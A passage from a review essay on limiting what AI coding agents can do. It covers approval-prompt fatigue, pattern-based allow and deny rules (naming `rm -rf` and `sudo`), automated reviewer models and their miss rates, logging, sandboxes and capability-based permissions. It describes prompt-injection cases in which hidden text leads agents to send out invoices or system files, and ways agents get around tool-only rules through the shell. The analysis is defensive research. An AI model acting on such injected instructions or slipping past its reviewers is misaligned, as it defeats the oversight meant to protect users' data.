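|---|---|---|
| Command | `npm test` | The text in package.json, plus any "pretest" and "posttest" commands, which npm runs automatically |
| Files | Usually none | The tests, every package they load, and anything else the user's account can read or change |
| Child programs | None | A shell, Node.js and whatever the tests start, such as a browser |
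| Connections | None | Databases, internal services and the internet |

*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao et al., 2026) collects 290 public reports of agents misusing their access to files, 158 with confirmed harm. Uninformative approval prompts contributed to 31 of the 290. Some commands were too short to show what they would do, such as `python3 setup.py`, which runs whatever is in the script. Others were too long to read easily. Codex sometimes wrapped a simple edit in a script with its own error checks, and its longest command had 330 characters.

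The researchers also built 11 small projects in which a routine command had a hidden destructive effect, such as a code checker that deleted source files. Claude Code, running the older model Sonnet 4.6, let the damage happen in 10 of them. Codex asked to run the commands outside its sandbox, but its requests didn't mention the hidden effects.

### Rules that match the text of a command

To reduce approval prompts, agents compare each command with lists of patterns. The coding agent in *An Empirical Study of Harness Design for Coding Agents* (2026) runs `ls` (list a folder) and `cat` (print a file) without asking. By default it rejects `rm -rf` (delete a folder and its contents), `sudo` (run with administrator rights) and `git push` (publish code).

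Zhong and colleagues attribute 52 reports partly to filters that examined a command's text rather than its effect. A rule that looks only for the word `cat` treats a file of passwords the same way as a README, and blocking `rm` doesn't stop a model from deleting the same files from Python. In another common failure, with 77 reports, the rules covered the agent's built-in file tools but not the shell, so an agent that couldn't open a file with its own tool could print it with `cat`.

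Users add to these lists by choosing "don't ask again", but it is hard to make a rule that is neither too broad nor too narrow. In one case, Codex offered to stop asking about `sed -i`, which would have let it edit any file in place. A rule matching the whole command would have been useless, since the agent was unlikely to write exactly the same script again.

Even a narrow rule, such as one that allows `npm test`, permits whatever test script package.json contains when the command runs. An agent that can edit the project's files can change that script, then run the command the user has already approved.

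Many users choose very broad rules. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule allowing some shell commands by June 2026. Many of these rules allowed any Python or Node.js script, which Anthropic considers essentially the same as allowing every command. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks turned off altogether.

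### Why repeated requests lose their value

Claude Code users approved 93% of permission prompts according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, and 97% according to the company's later article. Most requests are probably harmless, so these rates don't prove that users were careless. Users also rejected 39% of the plans that Claude presented for approval, so they don't accept everything.

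In one experiment, Anthropic paid 1,053 testers to work on coding tasks and replaced one approval prompt in each session with a request to run a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

The testers weren't working on their own projects and had little to lose, so developers might be more careful with their own work. People who approve without reading also get through more prompts, so some of the decline could reflect which testers reached 50. Anthropic also used the results to promote its own alternative to manual approval. Even so, a rejection rate this low suggests that prompts are not a dependable safeguard.

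*Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) asked 107 practitioners how they handle permission requests. Of these, 47.7% said they read them carefully, 33.6% skim them, and 20.6% approve by default. A third had become less careful over time. One interviewee complained that "every 10 seconds I have to click something".

A similar pattern appears when people review agents' finished code. *Habituation at the Gate* (2026) followed 400 people who repeatedly reviewed code changes proposed by agents. Their approval rate rose from 30.1% in earlier reviews to 36.8% in later ones, and the share of reviews requesting changes halved to 5.6%. Some of this shift could be justified if the agents' code improved.

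### Giving people better information

More informative prompts can help, but they take longer to read. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who tells an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. Hidden instructions in a supplier's note lead the agent to copy the raw invoices into "report.csv", which it then asks to send to the auditor. The recipient and file name look fine, so the problem is visible only to someone who knows how the agent made the file.

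The researchers asked 80 volunteers to judge requests like this, using one of four kinds of prompt.

| What the prompt contained | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| The arguments, the user's original instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
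| The same facts, organised around the action's consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

The difference in unsafe approvals between the last two rows could be due to chance. Even with the best prompt, people approved about a quarter of the unsafe requests, and answering 100 of those prompts at the same speed would take 55 minutes.

Users can also set permissions in advance. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, asked 113 people without software backgrounds to supervise a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had requested. One group first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories, such as spending money or deleting something. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, then approved many of the excessive actions when prompted. These approvals accounted for 133 of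 the 148 excessive actions that went ahead in this group.

People who judged every action individually blocked 20 percentage points more of the excessive actions than the group with rules. But they saw only 18 prompts, so they may not have had time to tire of them.

### Automated reviewers

Claude Code originally prompted the user before every file change and shell command. In March 2026, Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026) introduced a mode in which a separate model reviews actions instead of the user. Anthropic made this mode the default on several plans in August, and *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) lists it as the starting mode on every plan from version 2.1.283.

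Anthropic explains that Claude can read files and edit project files without review. Shell commands, web requests and most other actions go to a reviewing model, which first makes a quick yes-or-no decision. If that decision is to block the action, the model reviews it again with more reasoning. When an action is blocked, Claude receives the reason and looks for a safer approach. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, Claude Code asks the user.

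The reviewer receives the user's messages and Claude's tool calls, but not Claude's explanations or the tools' output. This keeps Claude from persuading the reviewer to make a bad decision and shields it from most injected text, but it also leaves the reviewer with less information. If Claude edits package.json and then runs `npm test`, the reviewer can take the edit into account. If a dangerous entry was already in the file, the reviewer gets only the command `npm test`, just as a user would.

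Outside researchers have also tested the reviewers. In *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026) gave Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code 128 maintenance tasks, such as cancelling jobs and deleting old files. The table combines their results with Anthropic's.

| Actions tested | Agent | Unwanted actions approved | Legitimate actions blocked |
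|---|---|---|---|
| 52 real cases of Claude exceeding its instructions | Claude Code | 17% | 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls |
| 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out | Claude Code | 5.7% | As above |
| Dangerous commands from the experiment with testers | Claude Code | 11% | Not reported |
| Maintenance tasks | Claude Code | 54% | 37% |
| Maintenance tasks | Codex | 93% | 10% |
| Maintenance tasks | Qwen Code | 80% | 31% |

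The first figure comes from only 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be between 9% and 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, it took a request to "clean up the PR" (pull request, a proposed code change) as permission to overwrite the project's history.

The maintenance tasks produced much worse results because the requests left out important rules. In one, a user asks the agent to delete old experiment files for a range of tickets. The benchmark's answer key permits deleting only that user's files, but the request doesn't include this limit. Yang and colleagues found that 132 of the 143 unwanted actions broke a rule that appeared in neither the request nor the tools' output. A careful person with the same information would probably have approved many of those actions too.

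When the researchers added the missing rules to the requests, the reviewers approved 8–26% of the unwanted actions and blocked only 2–3% of the legitimate ones. Using stronger models as reviewers helped much less. Claude Opus 5.5 appeared to reduce Claude Code's misses from 10 in 24 to one, but only because it refused to complete the second stage of any review, and Claude Code treats that refusal as a block. With the rules stated from the start, the agents proposed no unwanted actions in 384 new runs.

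The main weakness therefore seems to be that nobody has worked out what access the task requires. Reviewers can enforce a stated limit reasonably well, but they are poor at guessing what the limit should be.

Tests with hidden instructions gave better results. In an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned, none of 720 attacks succeeded against its latest models in auto mode. But an average of only 0.09% succeeded when the same models ran without permission checks, so the models themselves resisted nearly all the attacks. Automated review made a clearer difference for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, reducing the attack success rate from 19.03% to 5.83%.

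### Three records of one run

Suppose the user approves `npm test` in the second project and it empties the live database. There could be three records of what happened.

| | Agent's transcript | Application's log | System-call trace |
|---|---|---|---|
| What it holds | Messages, tool calls and the output returned to the model | Permission decisions, and when each tool call started and ended | Processes, files opened and connections made |
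| What it would contain here | `npm test`, followed by "12 tests passed" | The user approved the command, and it finished without an error | A shell started Node.js twice, and the first copy connected to a database |
| What is missing | Anything the command did without printing it | What happened inside the command | Why the command ran, and usually what it told the database to do |

An agent's transcript isn't a reliable record of what ran. *Harness Self-Evolution for Long-Horizon Terminal Agents* (2026) notes that the agent program may never start a command the model requested, or may return only part of the command's output. *Do Tool Calls Execute as Intended?* (2026) examines how the code that passes a command to the shell can change the command's text. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026) points out that if a transcript contains the same payment instruction twice, a reader may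 not be able to tell whether the payment went through once or twice.

An application's log can settle some of these questions. Agentao, a program for running agents, is designed to record a permission decision for every tool call the model attempts, according to *Agentao* (2026). If the call goes ahead, the log also records its start and whether it succeeded. But an ordinary application log contains only the events that the application's developers chose to log. It doesn't automatically include events inside a child process, such as the one that ran the database script.

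### Linking an operation to the tool call that caused it

A system-call trace does cover child processes, but it can contain thousands of operations with no indication of their purpose. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) describes a tool of the same name that tries to connect these operations to the model's requests. The tool collects system calls and reads the agent's traffic with the model before encryption or after decryption. It does both with eBPF, a Linux feature for running small, pre-checked programs inside the kernel when chosen events occur.

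AgentSight then looks for three kinds of link. It tracks which process started which, checks whether an operation happened within 100–500 milliseconds of a model's response, and looks for text, such as a file name, that appears in both the response and a system call. In the example, timing and matching text could connect the model's request to the start of `npm test`, but they might miss the database connection, which could happen seconds later and use an address that wasn't in the response. The chain of processes from npm to the database script would link that connection to the request.

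In one test, a web page contained hidden instructions that led an agent to send a system file to an outside server. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37, and a second language model correctly identified the attack. The test shows that the method can work, but Zheng and colleagues don't report how often it raises false alarms.

AgentSight slowed three development tasks by 0.4–4.9%, or 2.9% on average. These figures are rough because the researchers ran each task only three times with the tool and three times without it. The largest slowdown was about one second on a 23-second task, and a model's response time could easily vary by that much.

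Following the chain of processes fails when processes are connected through a file, such as a test that an agent edits and a developer runs the next day. To handle such cases, *Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) marks the agent's process, its child processes and every file they write. Any process that later reads a marked file is marked too. These marks form a provenance record, which shows where a file or an action came from.

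In a test of Agent-Warden, an agent's script wrote and renamed a file, which an unrelated program later read. Langfuse, a popular tool for logging agents' activity, did not connect that program to the agent. Agent-Warden reconstructed the whole chain in all 120 runs, 30 for each of two versions on each of two computers. It added 0.2–3.5% to the running time of a separate workload that rapidly created processes and files.

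Agent-Warden's coverage is narrow, however. It doesn't track network connections, so it would miss the one to the database. It also misses some ways of using files, such as mapping a file into a program's memory. The marks disappear when the computer restarts. They can also spread too far, because when a marked process ends, it passes its mark to its parent, even if the parent used none of its data.

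### What a log can do after the damage

With the right records, people can reconstruct an incident and prevent it from happening again. In the example, besides the three records above, they would need to know what package.json contained at the time and which database the environment variable pointed to.

Assigning responsibility fairly would require the same information. The application's log correctly records that the user approved `npm test`, but the user may not have known that the command would delete the company's records.

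Even a careful log can leave an action's outcome uncertain. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* gives the example of an agent that asks a service to create a support ticket. The service creates it, but the agent program crashes before recording the result. If the agent tries again after restarting, it may create a second ticket.

Zhang (2026), in *Agent libOS*, proposes recording each external action before it starts. If the system crashes before confirming the result, it marks the outcome as unknown and doesn't automatically repeat the action. Zhang also separates records from permissions, so a log entry showing that the user approved an action yesterday can't authorise it today.

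Logs also need protection. Goel recommends recording every tool call, but a log can leak secrets. If it is an ordinary file in the user's account, generated code can also change or delete it. Zhang acknowledges that an administrator with direct access to Agent libOS's database could alter its records.

Above all, a log can't undo the actions it records. AgentSight's second model analysed the attack only after the agent had sent the file. Of the reports in which Zhong and colleagues could tell whether recovery was possible, 40% involved permanent loss.

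Their own design, YoloFS, stores file changes separately until the user accepts them, so the changes can be reversed. After each command, the agent receives a list of the files that changed and can restore an earlier version. When Claude Code used YoloFS on the 11 projects with hidden effects, it noticed and reversed the damage in eight. In the other three it treated the changes as normal, but the user could still reject them.

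YoloFS also asks for permission before a command reads certain files, because reading a password can't be undone. It protects only files, so it couldn't restore a remote database that `npm test` had emptied or recall data that a script had already sent.

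## Runtimes and permissions that start from no access

Most sandboxes for agents take a process with the user's full access and remove some of it. The opposite approach starts code with no access and gives it named resources one at a time. Pydantic, which makes tools for Python developers, calls the usual method "working backwards" and compares its own to a firewall that blocks all traffic except what someone has listed.

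Both methods could end up giving a script the same access, but mistakes are easier to notice when the script starts with none. A forgotten grant makes the script fail, so the developer finds out quickly, whereas a forgotten restriction leaves a file or host exposed, and nobody may notice until it causes harm. Saltzer and Schroeder made the same case for access control in general in 1975.

### An agent that runs only WebAssembly

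WebAssembly is a format for compiled programs, originally designed for web browsers. A WebAssembly program can calculate within its own memory but can't make system calls. To read a file, it has to call a function that its runtime supplies. If the runtime supplies no such function, the program can't read files.

*wasm-agent* (Monperrus, 2026) describes a prototype coding agent built around this property. The agent has ordinary tools for reading and editing files, but no shell, and it can't run Python. To run anything, it has to write a program in Rust, compile it to WebAssembly and run the result in Wasmtime, a WebAssembly runtime. The compiler only translates the program, so the agent's code doesn't run until it is inside Wasmtime.

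By default, the program can do little more than calculate and print text. If it needs files, the agent has to name a folder when it requests the run. For a program that totals the sales records, the log entry might look like this:

```json
{"name": "wasmtime_exec",
 "arguments": {"path": "total.wasm", "dirs": "sales::/work"}}
```

The "path" field identifies the program. The "dirs" field gives it access to the folder "sales", which appears to the program as "/work". Wasmtime opens this folder before the program starts, and the program can't reach any file outside it.

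The same entry therefore grants the access and records it. Someone who reads the log a month later can tell, without reading the program, that the run changed nothing outside "sales", which they couldn't tell from an entry for `npm test`. The agent's editing tools also name each file they change, so the whole log lists every place where the agent could have changed something.

However, an entry shows only the limits of what the program could do. It doesn't show which files in "sales" changed, and the program can read the customers' names as well as the amounts. The model also chooses the folders, so an injected instruction could lead it to name the user's home directory. Monperrus points out that a supervising program could reject any folder outside the project without understanding Rust. Without such a rule, the problem would appear in the log only afterwards.

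Each run also has an instruction budget, which Wasmtime calls fuel. The default is 20 billion units, and each WebAssembly instruction uses one. When the fuel runs out, Wasmtime stops the program. Fuel use doesn't depend on how busy the computer is, whereas a time limit might stop a healthy program on a busy computer. In a demonstration with a smaller budget, Wasmtime stopped an infinite loop after a billion instructions. A program that updates two files could still run out of fuel after updating the first, so Monperrus's claim that this leaves nothing half-applied is too strong.

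The design has substantial drawbacks. Without a shell or a network connection, generated code can't run Git or npm, or contact a database. The agent can download the source code of Rust packages, but it has to build them into its own program by hand. In one run, it downloaded a package for reading JSON, a common data format, and found that the package required an experimental version of the compiler, so it switched to tinyjson, which has four files and no dependencies.

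Many popular packages are harder to use because they have build scripts, which run during compilation, or procedural macros, which the compiler runs to generate code. Both would normally run outside Wasmtime with the user's full access, much as npm's setup scripts did. The prototype supports neither, and Monperrus's current answer is to pick a different package. The published demonstrations are small programs that list prime numbers, sort lines and edit JSON, so it is unclear how much ordinary programming the agent could do.

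The same approach can work for tools. Microsoft's Wassette runs WebAssembly components as MCP tools and denies them access to system resources by default. It could restrict tools that would otherwise run on the user's computer with full access, but developers have to compile them to WebAssembly first.

### Interpreters that expose only chosen functions

Pydantic's Monty, a new interpreter for a subset of Python, lets agents write Python instead of Rust. Its developers left out the dangerous parts of the standard interpreter, which Stinner's pysandbox had tried to hide. By default, a script can read the clock but cannot open files or connections or start other programs. A developer can attach chosen folders and provide host functions, which the script can call but which run outside the sandbox.

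Suppose a developer provides this host function:

```python
def get_amounts():
    with open("sales.csv") as file:
        return [float(row["amount"]) for row in csv.DictReader(file)]
```

The model can then total the sales with `sum(get_amounts())`. When the script calls `get_amounts()`, Monty pauses the script and the agent program runs the function with its full access. The script receives only a list of numbers, not the customers' names in the same file, so this limits access more precisely than any rule about whole files.

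Now suppose the developer provides a more flexible function instead:

```python
def read_file(path):
    with open(path) as file:
        return file.read()
```

This function has the same access as the first, but the script chooses the path, so the script can read any file the user can, including credential files. Tymshare's compiler had the same problem. A function that fetches any web address gives the script similarly broad network access, and one that runs shell commands restores nearly all the access that Monty removed.

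Pydantic's *Security Model* warns that Monty "cannot guarantee that what you handed it is safe" and tells developers to check the arguments of host functions as they would any other untrusted input. Broad functions are tempting because developers don't have to predict what an agent will need, which is also why shell tools are popular.

Varda, Pai and Gupta, in *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster*, describe a similar design for JavaScript at Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company. The design runs each script in an isolate, a separate instance of the JavaScript engine in Google's Chrome browser. An isolate starts in a few milliseconds, so a company can create one for every script and discard it afterward. The developer passes in objects with selected functions, such as a chat room that lets the script read and post messages.

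Varda and colleagues prefer these purpose-built functions to filtering web requests, because a filter has to interpret every request to an existing service. With a purpose-built interface, the developer can leave out unwanted operations and could, for example, let a script read social media posts but not publish them.

Cloudflare's design doesn't always start from no access. AutoClaw's *Dynamic Workers* notes that if a developer leaves out the network setting, an isolate generally inherits the network access of the program that created it.

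| | Monperrus's prototype | Monty | Cloudflare's isolates |
|---|---|---|---|
| Language | Rust | A subset of Python | Mainly JavaScript |
| How code gets access | The agent names folders | The developer attaches folders and provides functions | The developer provides objects with functions |
| Network | None | Only through host functions | Blocked, filtered or inherited, depending on the setting |
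| Outside packages | Small ones without build scripts | None inside the sandbox | JavaScript packages bundled with the script |

Security also depends on the runtime itself. Varda and colleagues acknowledge that security bugs are more common in Chrome's JavaScript engine than in typical software for running virtual machines, so Cloudflare adds other layers of protection. In Monty's first public hacking contest, someone escaped in under 48 hours by exploiting a memory error. According to Pydantic's *Hack Monty Round 3 & Round 2 results*, nobody escaped in the second contest, which began in late May 2026.

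Pydantic has since moved Monty into a separate process, which starts with no secrets in its environment. Code that escaped would no longer be in the agent's memory, but it would still be on the same machine, so Pydantic also offers a version that runs on a different computer.

Monty, Pydantic's sandbox, is fast but limited. Pydantic reports in *Monty* that a new sandbox starts in 0.8 milliseconds, compared with 195 milliseconds for a local Docker container. The comparison favours Monty because it uses a process prepared in advance, while the container starts from nothing. Pydantic advises using a container or a virtual machine for coding agents that install packages or run build tools.

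### Limiting what a credential can do

Code with almost no access to the user's computer can still do serious damage with a powerful token, such as the one used in the PocketOS deletion.

Developers can limit a token to certain resources. Railway's *Public API* lists a project token that works in only one environment, so a token for staging should not have worked on the live database. A project token for the live site might still have allowed the deletion. Crane needed a token only for domain operations, and one limited to those would have prevented the deletion. Tom's Hardware reported that Railway planned to reassess how precisely its tokens limit permissions.

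A short token lifetime is less dependable. If the token had expired soon after Crane finished with it, it would have been useless when the agent found it, but expiry would not have helped if the agent had found it earlier.

Another option is a token that carries only the rights of the person the agent is working for. This is most useful when one agent serves many people. If the agent has a single account that can read every employee's files, one employee might get it to fetch another's. If the agent instead used the token of the employee making the request, the file service would refuse. Such a token wouldn't have saved PocketOS's database, because the company's founder had the right to delete it. OAuth, a standard that Railway also supports, lets users grant an application only some of their rights, but that helps only if the service offers a narrow enough permission.

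A credential proxy keeps the secret away from the code altogether. Claude Code can do this by giving commands a placeholder in place of the secret. Cloudflare lets developers add a key to each web request after it leaves the isolate. *Cloudflare says containers are too slow for AI agent sandboxing* describes a method like Claude Code's in the open-source agent IronCurtain.

Hiding Crane's token this way would not have prevented the deletion, because code could still have used it at Railway. Checking the web address wouldn't have helped either, because the deletion request that Abdelwahab published went to a general-purpose address and only its body identified it as a deletion. A proxy would have had to read the body and know which operations to refuse. It would have been simpler to give the agent a host function that used the token but could only change domains, provided the agent couldn't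 reach another copy of the token.

### Who decides what a task needs

All these designs can enforce a limit, but somebody has to choose it. Choosing a limit is easy for a script that adds up one column and much harder for a coding task, where the agent may not know which files it needs until it has read some of them. Three systems published in 2026 divide this decision between people, models and fixed rules in different ways.

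*Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, June 2026) relies on a written contract for each task. Suppose an agent has to add a timeout option to a program. The contract lets it edit "api.py" from the start and request access to "serialization.py" if the change spreads there, but forbids it from reading an unrelated file of packaging notes. PORTICO, a program between the model and its tools, checks each request against the contract. If PORTICO approves the request, the model receives a handle (a capability for that file) on its next turn.

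PORTICO withdraws the handle when the reason for it ends, for example when the tests pass. PORTICO runs the tests itself, because a model's report that they passed could be wrong. After PORTICO closes a temporary permission α, the agent must not be able to use it. Formally, α ∉ *V*<sub>t</sub> for all *t* ≥ *c*, where *V*<sub>t</sub> is the set of permissions the agent can use at turn *t* and *c* is the first turn after PORTICO closes α. The model may still have the file's name, but it can no longer use the name to access the file.

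*LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source* (Zheng, Zhang and Mao, 2026) describes IntentCap, which doesn't need a contract for each task. A model proposes a lease, a short-lived permission for one operation, and a checker with fixed rules accepts or rejects it. Each part of the lease must come from the right source. For instance, only the user can choose files and destinations, while a tool's description can define which arguments the tool accepts.

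Suppose a user asks an agent to extract tables from two PDFs and report the results in a named GitHub repository. One PDF contains hidden instructions to use an attacker's repository instead. The model may propose a lease for the attacker's repository, but the checker rejects it because that name doesn't appear in the user's request. Text from the PDF can still go into the report.

*AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, November 2026) has developers write a policy for each application. In its banking example, an agent must check the account balance before sending money. The agent then receives a single-use token that lasts 30 seconds. The recipient of the money can't come solely from untrusted text.

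AgentCap also limits what an agent can pass to a sub-agent. The sub-agent's token must cover the same action and resource as the parent's. It can't allow more uses or expire later than the parent's token, and the number of further times it can be passed on must be lower. This prevents a sub-agent from gaining more access than its parent, but the parent can't use these rules to narrow a permission from a whole folder to one file.

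| | PORTICO | IntentCap | AgentCap |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who sets the limits | Someone who writes a contract for the task | The user's request, within the limits of the tools and instructions | A developer who writes a policy for the application |
| What the model does | Requests extra access that the contract lists | Proposes a lease | Requests a token and states its purpose |
| When access ends | After an event such as passing tests | After use or at the expiry time | After a set time or number of uses |

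IntentCap needs the least preparation but depends on what the user says. If the user leaves out an important limit, the checker can't enforce it. Omitted limits were also the main difficulty for the automated reviewers in Yang and colleagues' tests.

All three systems also work only if actions pass through their checks. A script that opens files directly, in a process with the user's full access, would bypass a check on tool calls. PORTICO therefore tries to identify the effects of shell commands, and rejects or seeks approval for those it can't classify. IntentCap can translate leases into operating-system rules. Another solution would be to run scripts in an interpreter like Monty and put the checks in its host functions, since a script could reach anything outside the interpreter only through them.

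### What the limits prevent

To test revocation, Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that granted the same permissions but never withdrew them. In ten runs, the agent tried to reread a file after its permission should have ended. PORTICO refused every time, and the other version allowed it every time. In six more cases, a model was told to reuse old access to change files, alter Git data or contact a network host. PORTICO blocked all six actions, and the other version allowed them all. These tests show that revocation works, but they don't measure how often agents would misuse leftover access, because each test was designed to include an attempt.

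Another test had 17 scenarios with forbidden files or actions within reach, each run five times with Qwen3-Coder 30B, a small open-weight model. The agent broke the contract in every run with full access, in 86% of runs with a conventional sandbox, and in none with PORTICO. PORTICO's rules and the scoring both came from the contract, so this result shows that PORTICO enforced the contract but doesn't show whether the contract was a good one. In a separate test of 14 tasks from real software projects, the agent never broke the contract, even with full access.

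Zheng and colleagues replayed 3,746 recorded security-sensitive events from four existing benchmarks, and IntentCap accepted no unsafe action. When they treated all sources for the parts of a lease as equally trustworthy, the checker accepted 94% of the events it should have rejected. This is good evidence for separating the sources, but the researchers have not yet tested complete attacks on a running agent or attackers who adapt to the system.

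Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao did run complete attacks, 949 from AgentDojo and 1,054 from InjecAgent. Both benchmarks consist of simulated tasks in which tool results contain hidden instructions.

| Benchmark and model | Successful attacks, without and with AgentCap | User's task completed under attack, without and with AgentCap |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.6%, 5.1% | 73.6%, 74.9% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.2%, 0% | 75.7%, 75.0% |
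| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.2%, 8.6% | 74.1%, 69.9% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 12.0%, 0% | 73.0%, 69.9% |

Some of the remaining attacks aimed only to change the agent's written answer, which a check on tool calls can't prevent. Others used arguments or data that the policy did not mark as sensitive or untrusted. The researchers ran each test once and did not include attackers who knew how AgentCap worked, so the zeros don't show that it stops every attack.

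AgentCap also keeps a trust score for each agent. The score starts at 0.8, and every refused request multiplies it by 0.7. After three refusals it falls to about 0.27, which is below the threshold of 0.3, so the agent loses all its permissions. This limits an attacker's chances to probe the policy, but a harmless agent that made three forbidden requests by mistake would also lose its access.

### Whether useful agents need broad access

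In Santos-Grueiro's tests on 37 coding tasks, each run five times, the agent succeeded in 97% of runs with full access, 21% with a fixed, narrow set of permissions, and 87% when it could request the additional files listed in the contract. Most of the loss under fixed permissions therefore came from having no way to ask for more. The results support the common objection that an agent needs broad access to be useful because nobody can predict what it will need, but only when its permissions can't change.

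Revoking access sometimes prevented agents from finishing their tasks. In the main test, the agent completed all 14 tasks from real projects under every condition. But in additional tests with other models, agents completed 31 of 42 combinations of task and model under PORTICO, and all 42 under a version that never withdrew access. In some cases, access ended too early or the contract had no way to renew it, and in others the model failed to request it again. Santos-Grueiro suggests renewing access after a trusted event, such as a person's approval. This would bring back some approval prompts, but each could name a specific file and a reason.

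Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao found smaller losses. Without an attack, AgentCap reduced task completion by 2.0 to 7.2 percentage points, depending on the model and benchmark. They also compared it with Progent, an earlier system in which a model writes the policy for each task. With GPT-4o on AgentDojo, both systems stopped about the same share of attacks, but the agent completed 78% of ordinary tasks with AgentCap and 68% with Progent. Progent's policies often allowed only the values the model had predicted, so they blocked legitimate calls with other values.

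The comparison suggests that carefully written policies are worth the effort, but it may overstate their advantage. AgentCap's developers wrote their policies after reading descriptions of the benchmark's tasks, although they didn't change the policies in response to the results. A company writing a policy for its own staff would have to anticipate their requests.

IntentCap's usefulness is less well tested. It covered all 3,813 legitimate actions in one set of recordings, but Zheng and colleagues didn't measure how many tasks an agent could finish with it.

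The checks themselves take little time. AgentCap's take less than 0.2 milliseconds each, which is negligible compared with the time a model takes to respond. PORTICO adds a turn whenever it grants access, because the handle only becomes available on the next turn, and this probably takes longer. Zheng and colleagues haven't measured IntentCap's delay, which would include the time a model needs to propose each lease.

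These results weaken the case for giving agents full access by default, at least for tasks whose needs someone can describe. They provide less evidence about open-ended work, such as getting an unfamiliar project to run, where an agent may have to install packages and try many commands. A container with no valuable credentials is more practical for that work. The effort required to write the rules is also unknown. Santos-Grueiro found that eight templates covered all 70 test scenarios in one collection, but did not measure how long a contract takes to write or whether two people would write the same one.

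## Type systems that declare effects before code runs

PORTICO, Monty and similar systems check each request as it arrives, so a script may be half finished when one of them stops it. In some programming languages, a function's type includes the effects the function can have, so a compiler can reject a script that exceeds its limits before any of it runs. Types can also control where data goes after a script has read it, which a list of permitted files and hosts can't do.

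### Types that include effects

A type describes what kind of value something is, such as a number or a piece of text. A type checker, usually part of the compiler that translates a program into runnable form, compares the type each function requires with the type the program passes to it. If a function requires a number and the program passes it a list of names, the checker rejects the program without running it.

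In Python, JavaScript and most other mainstream languages, types leave out effects, which is why both versions of "count_rows" had the same signature. Haskell's types include them. These two Haskell functions add up the sales records:

```haskell
total :: [Double] -> Double
total amounts = sum amounts

saveTotal :: [Double] -> IO ()
saveTotal amounts = writeFile "total.txt" (show (sum amounts))
```

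The first line of each function gives its type. Both functions take a list of numbers, but the first function returns a number and the second has the result type `IO ()`. `IO` marks a computation that may use files, the network or anything else outside the program, and the empty brackets mean it returns no useful value.

The programmer can't simply leave `IO` out. The standard function "writeFile" has `IO` in its type, so any function that carries out the write or carries out "saveTotal" needs it too. If part of a program accepts only functions that turn a list of numbers into a number, the compiler accepts "total" there and rejects "saveTotal".

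Haskell's compiler only compares types, so it doesn't have to predict what a function will do. Like any sound checker, it also rejects some harmless programs. Haskell has a few functions that hide effects from the type checker, so code from a model has to use a restricted version called Safe Haskell, which excludes them.

Zhou and colleagues apply this to a calculator on a public website. For each question, a model writes a program that must have an integer type. If someone asks the calculator to delete every file on the server and then compute the factorial of 5, the model may write a program that does both. That program has an `IO` type, so the compiler rejects it.

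Haskell's `IO` covers every effect at once. Tan, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *ETAS*, present a language for agents whose signatures list individual effects:

```
tool read_source(path: string) -> string ![Repo.read]
```

The brackets at the end list the operations that the tool may request, here only reading from a project's repository. An agent with just this tool could review code but not change it. The researchers cite a Codex sub-agent that was told to do a read-only review but also generated an image and saved it outside the project. ETAS can also check the order of effects, for example that a request for approval comes before any change. If the compiler can't determine the order in advance, it adds a check that runs with the program.

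### How TACIT tracks capabilities

TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types), which Odersky and colleagues released in March 2026, records which file or connection a piece of code can use. It is an MCP server, so existing agents such as Claude Code can connect to it without modification. The agent sends TACIT a short Scala 3 program, and TACIT runs the program only if it passes the compiler's checks.

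In Scala, a capability is an ordinary value, such as an object that represents an open file. If a function uses a file called `f`, the compiler includes `f` in the function's capture set, which lists the capabilities the function may use. The capture set is part of the function's type:

| Type | What the function takes and returns | Capabilities it may use |
|---|---|---|
| `String -> Int` | Takes text and returns a whole number | None |
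| `String ->{f} Unit` | Takes text and returns no useful value | Only `f` |
| `String => Unit` | Takes text and returns no useful value | Any |

A function with an empty capture set is pure. The compiler accepts a pure function where the type allows more capabilities, but rejects a function that captures `f` where the type requires a pure one. Scala therefore has what Odersky and colleagues call local purity, which means most of a program can use files and the network while the compiler guarantees that one chosen part does not.

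TACIT's capabilities also expire. A program gets access to files by opening a block:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/work") {
  access("/work/total.txt").write("5120")
}
```

Inside the block, the program has a capability for the folder "/work". If an agent tries to keep this access by returning a function that opens a file later, the compiler rejects the program because the function's capture set would include the folder's capability, which exists only inside the block. Similar blocks grant access to named network hosts and commands.

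Some checks can only happen while the program runs. The compiler may not be able to determine which file path a program will use, so TACIT checks at run time that each path is inside "/work".

### Secrets that code can use but not send

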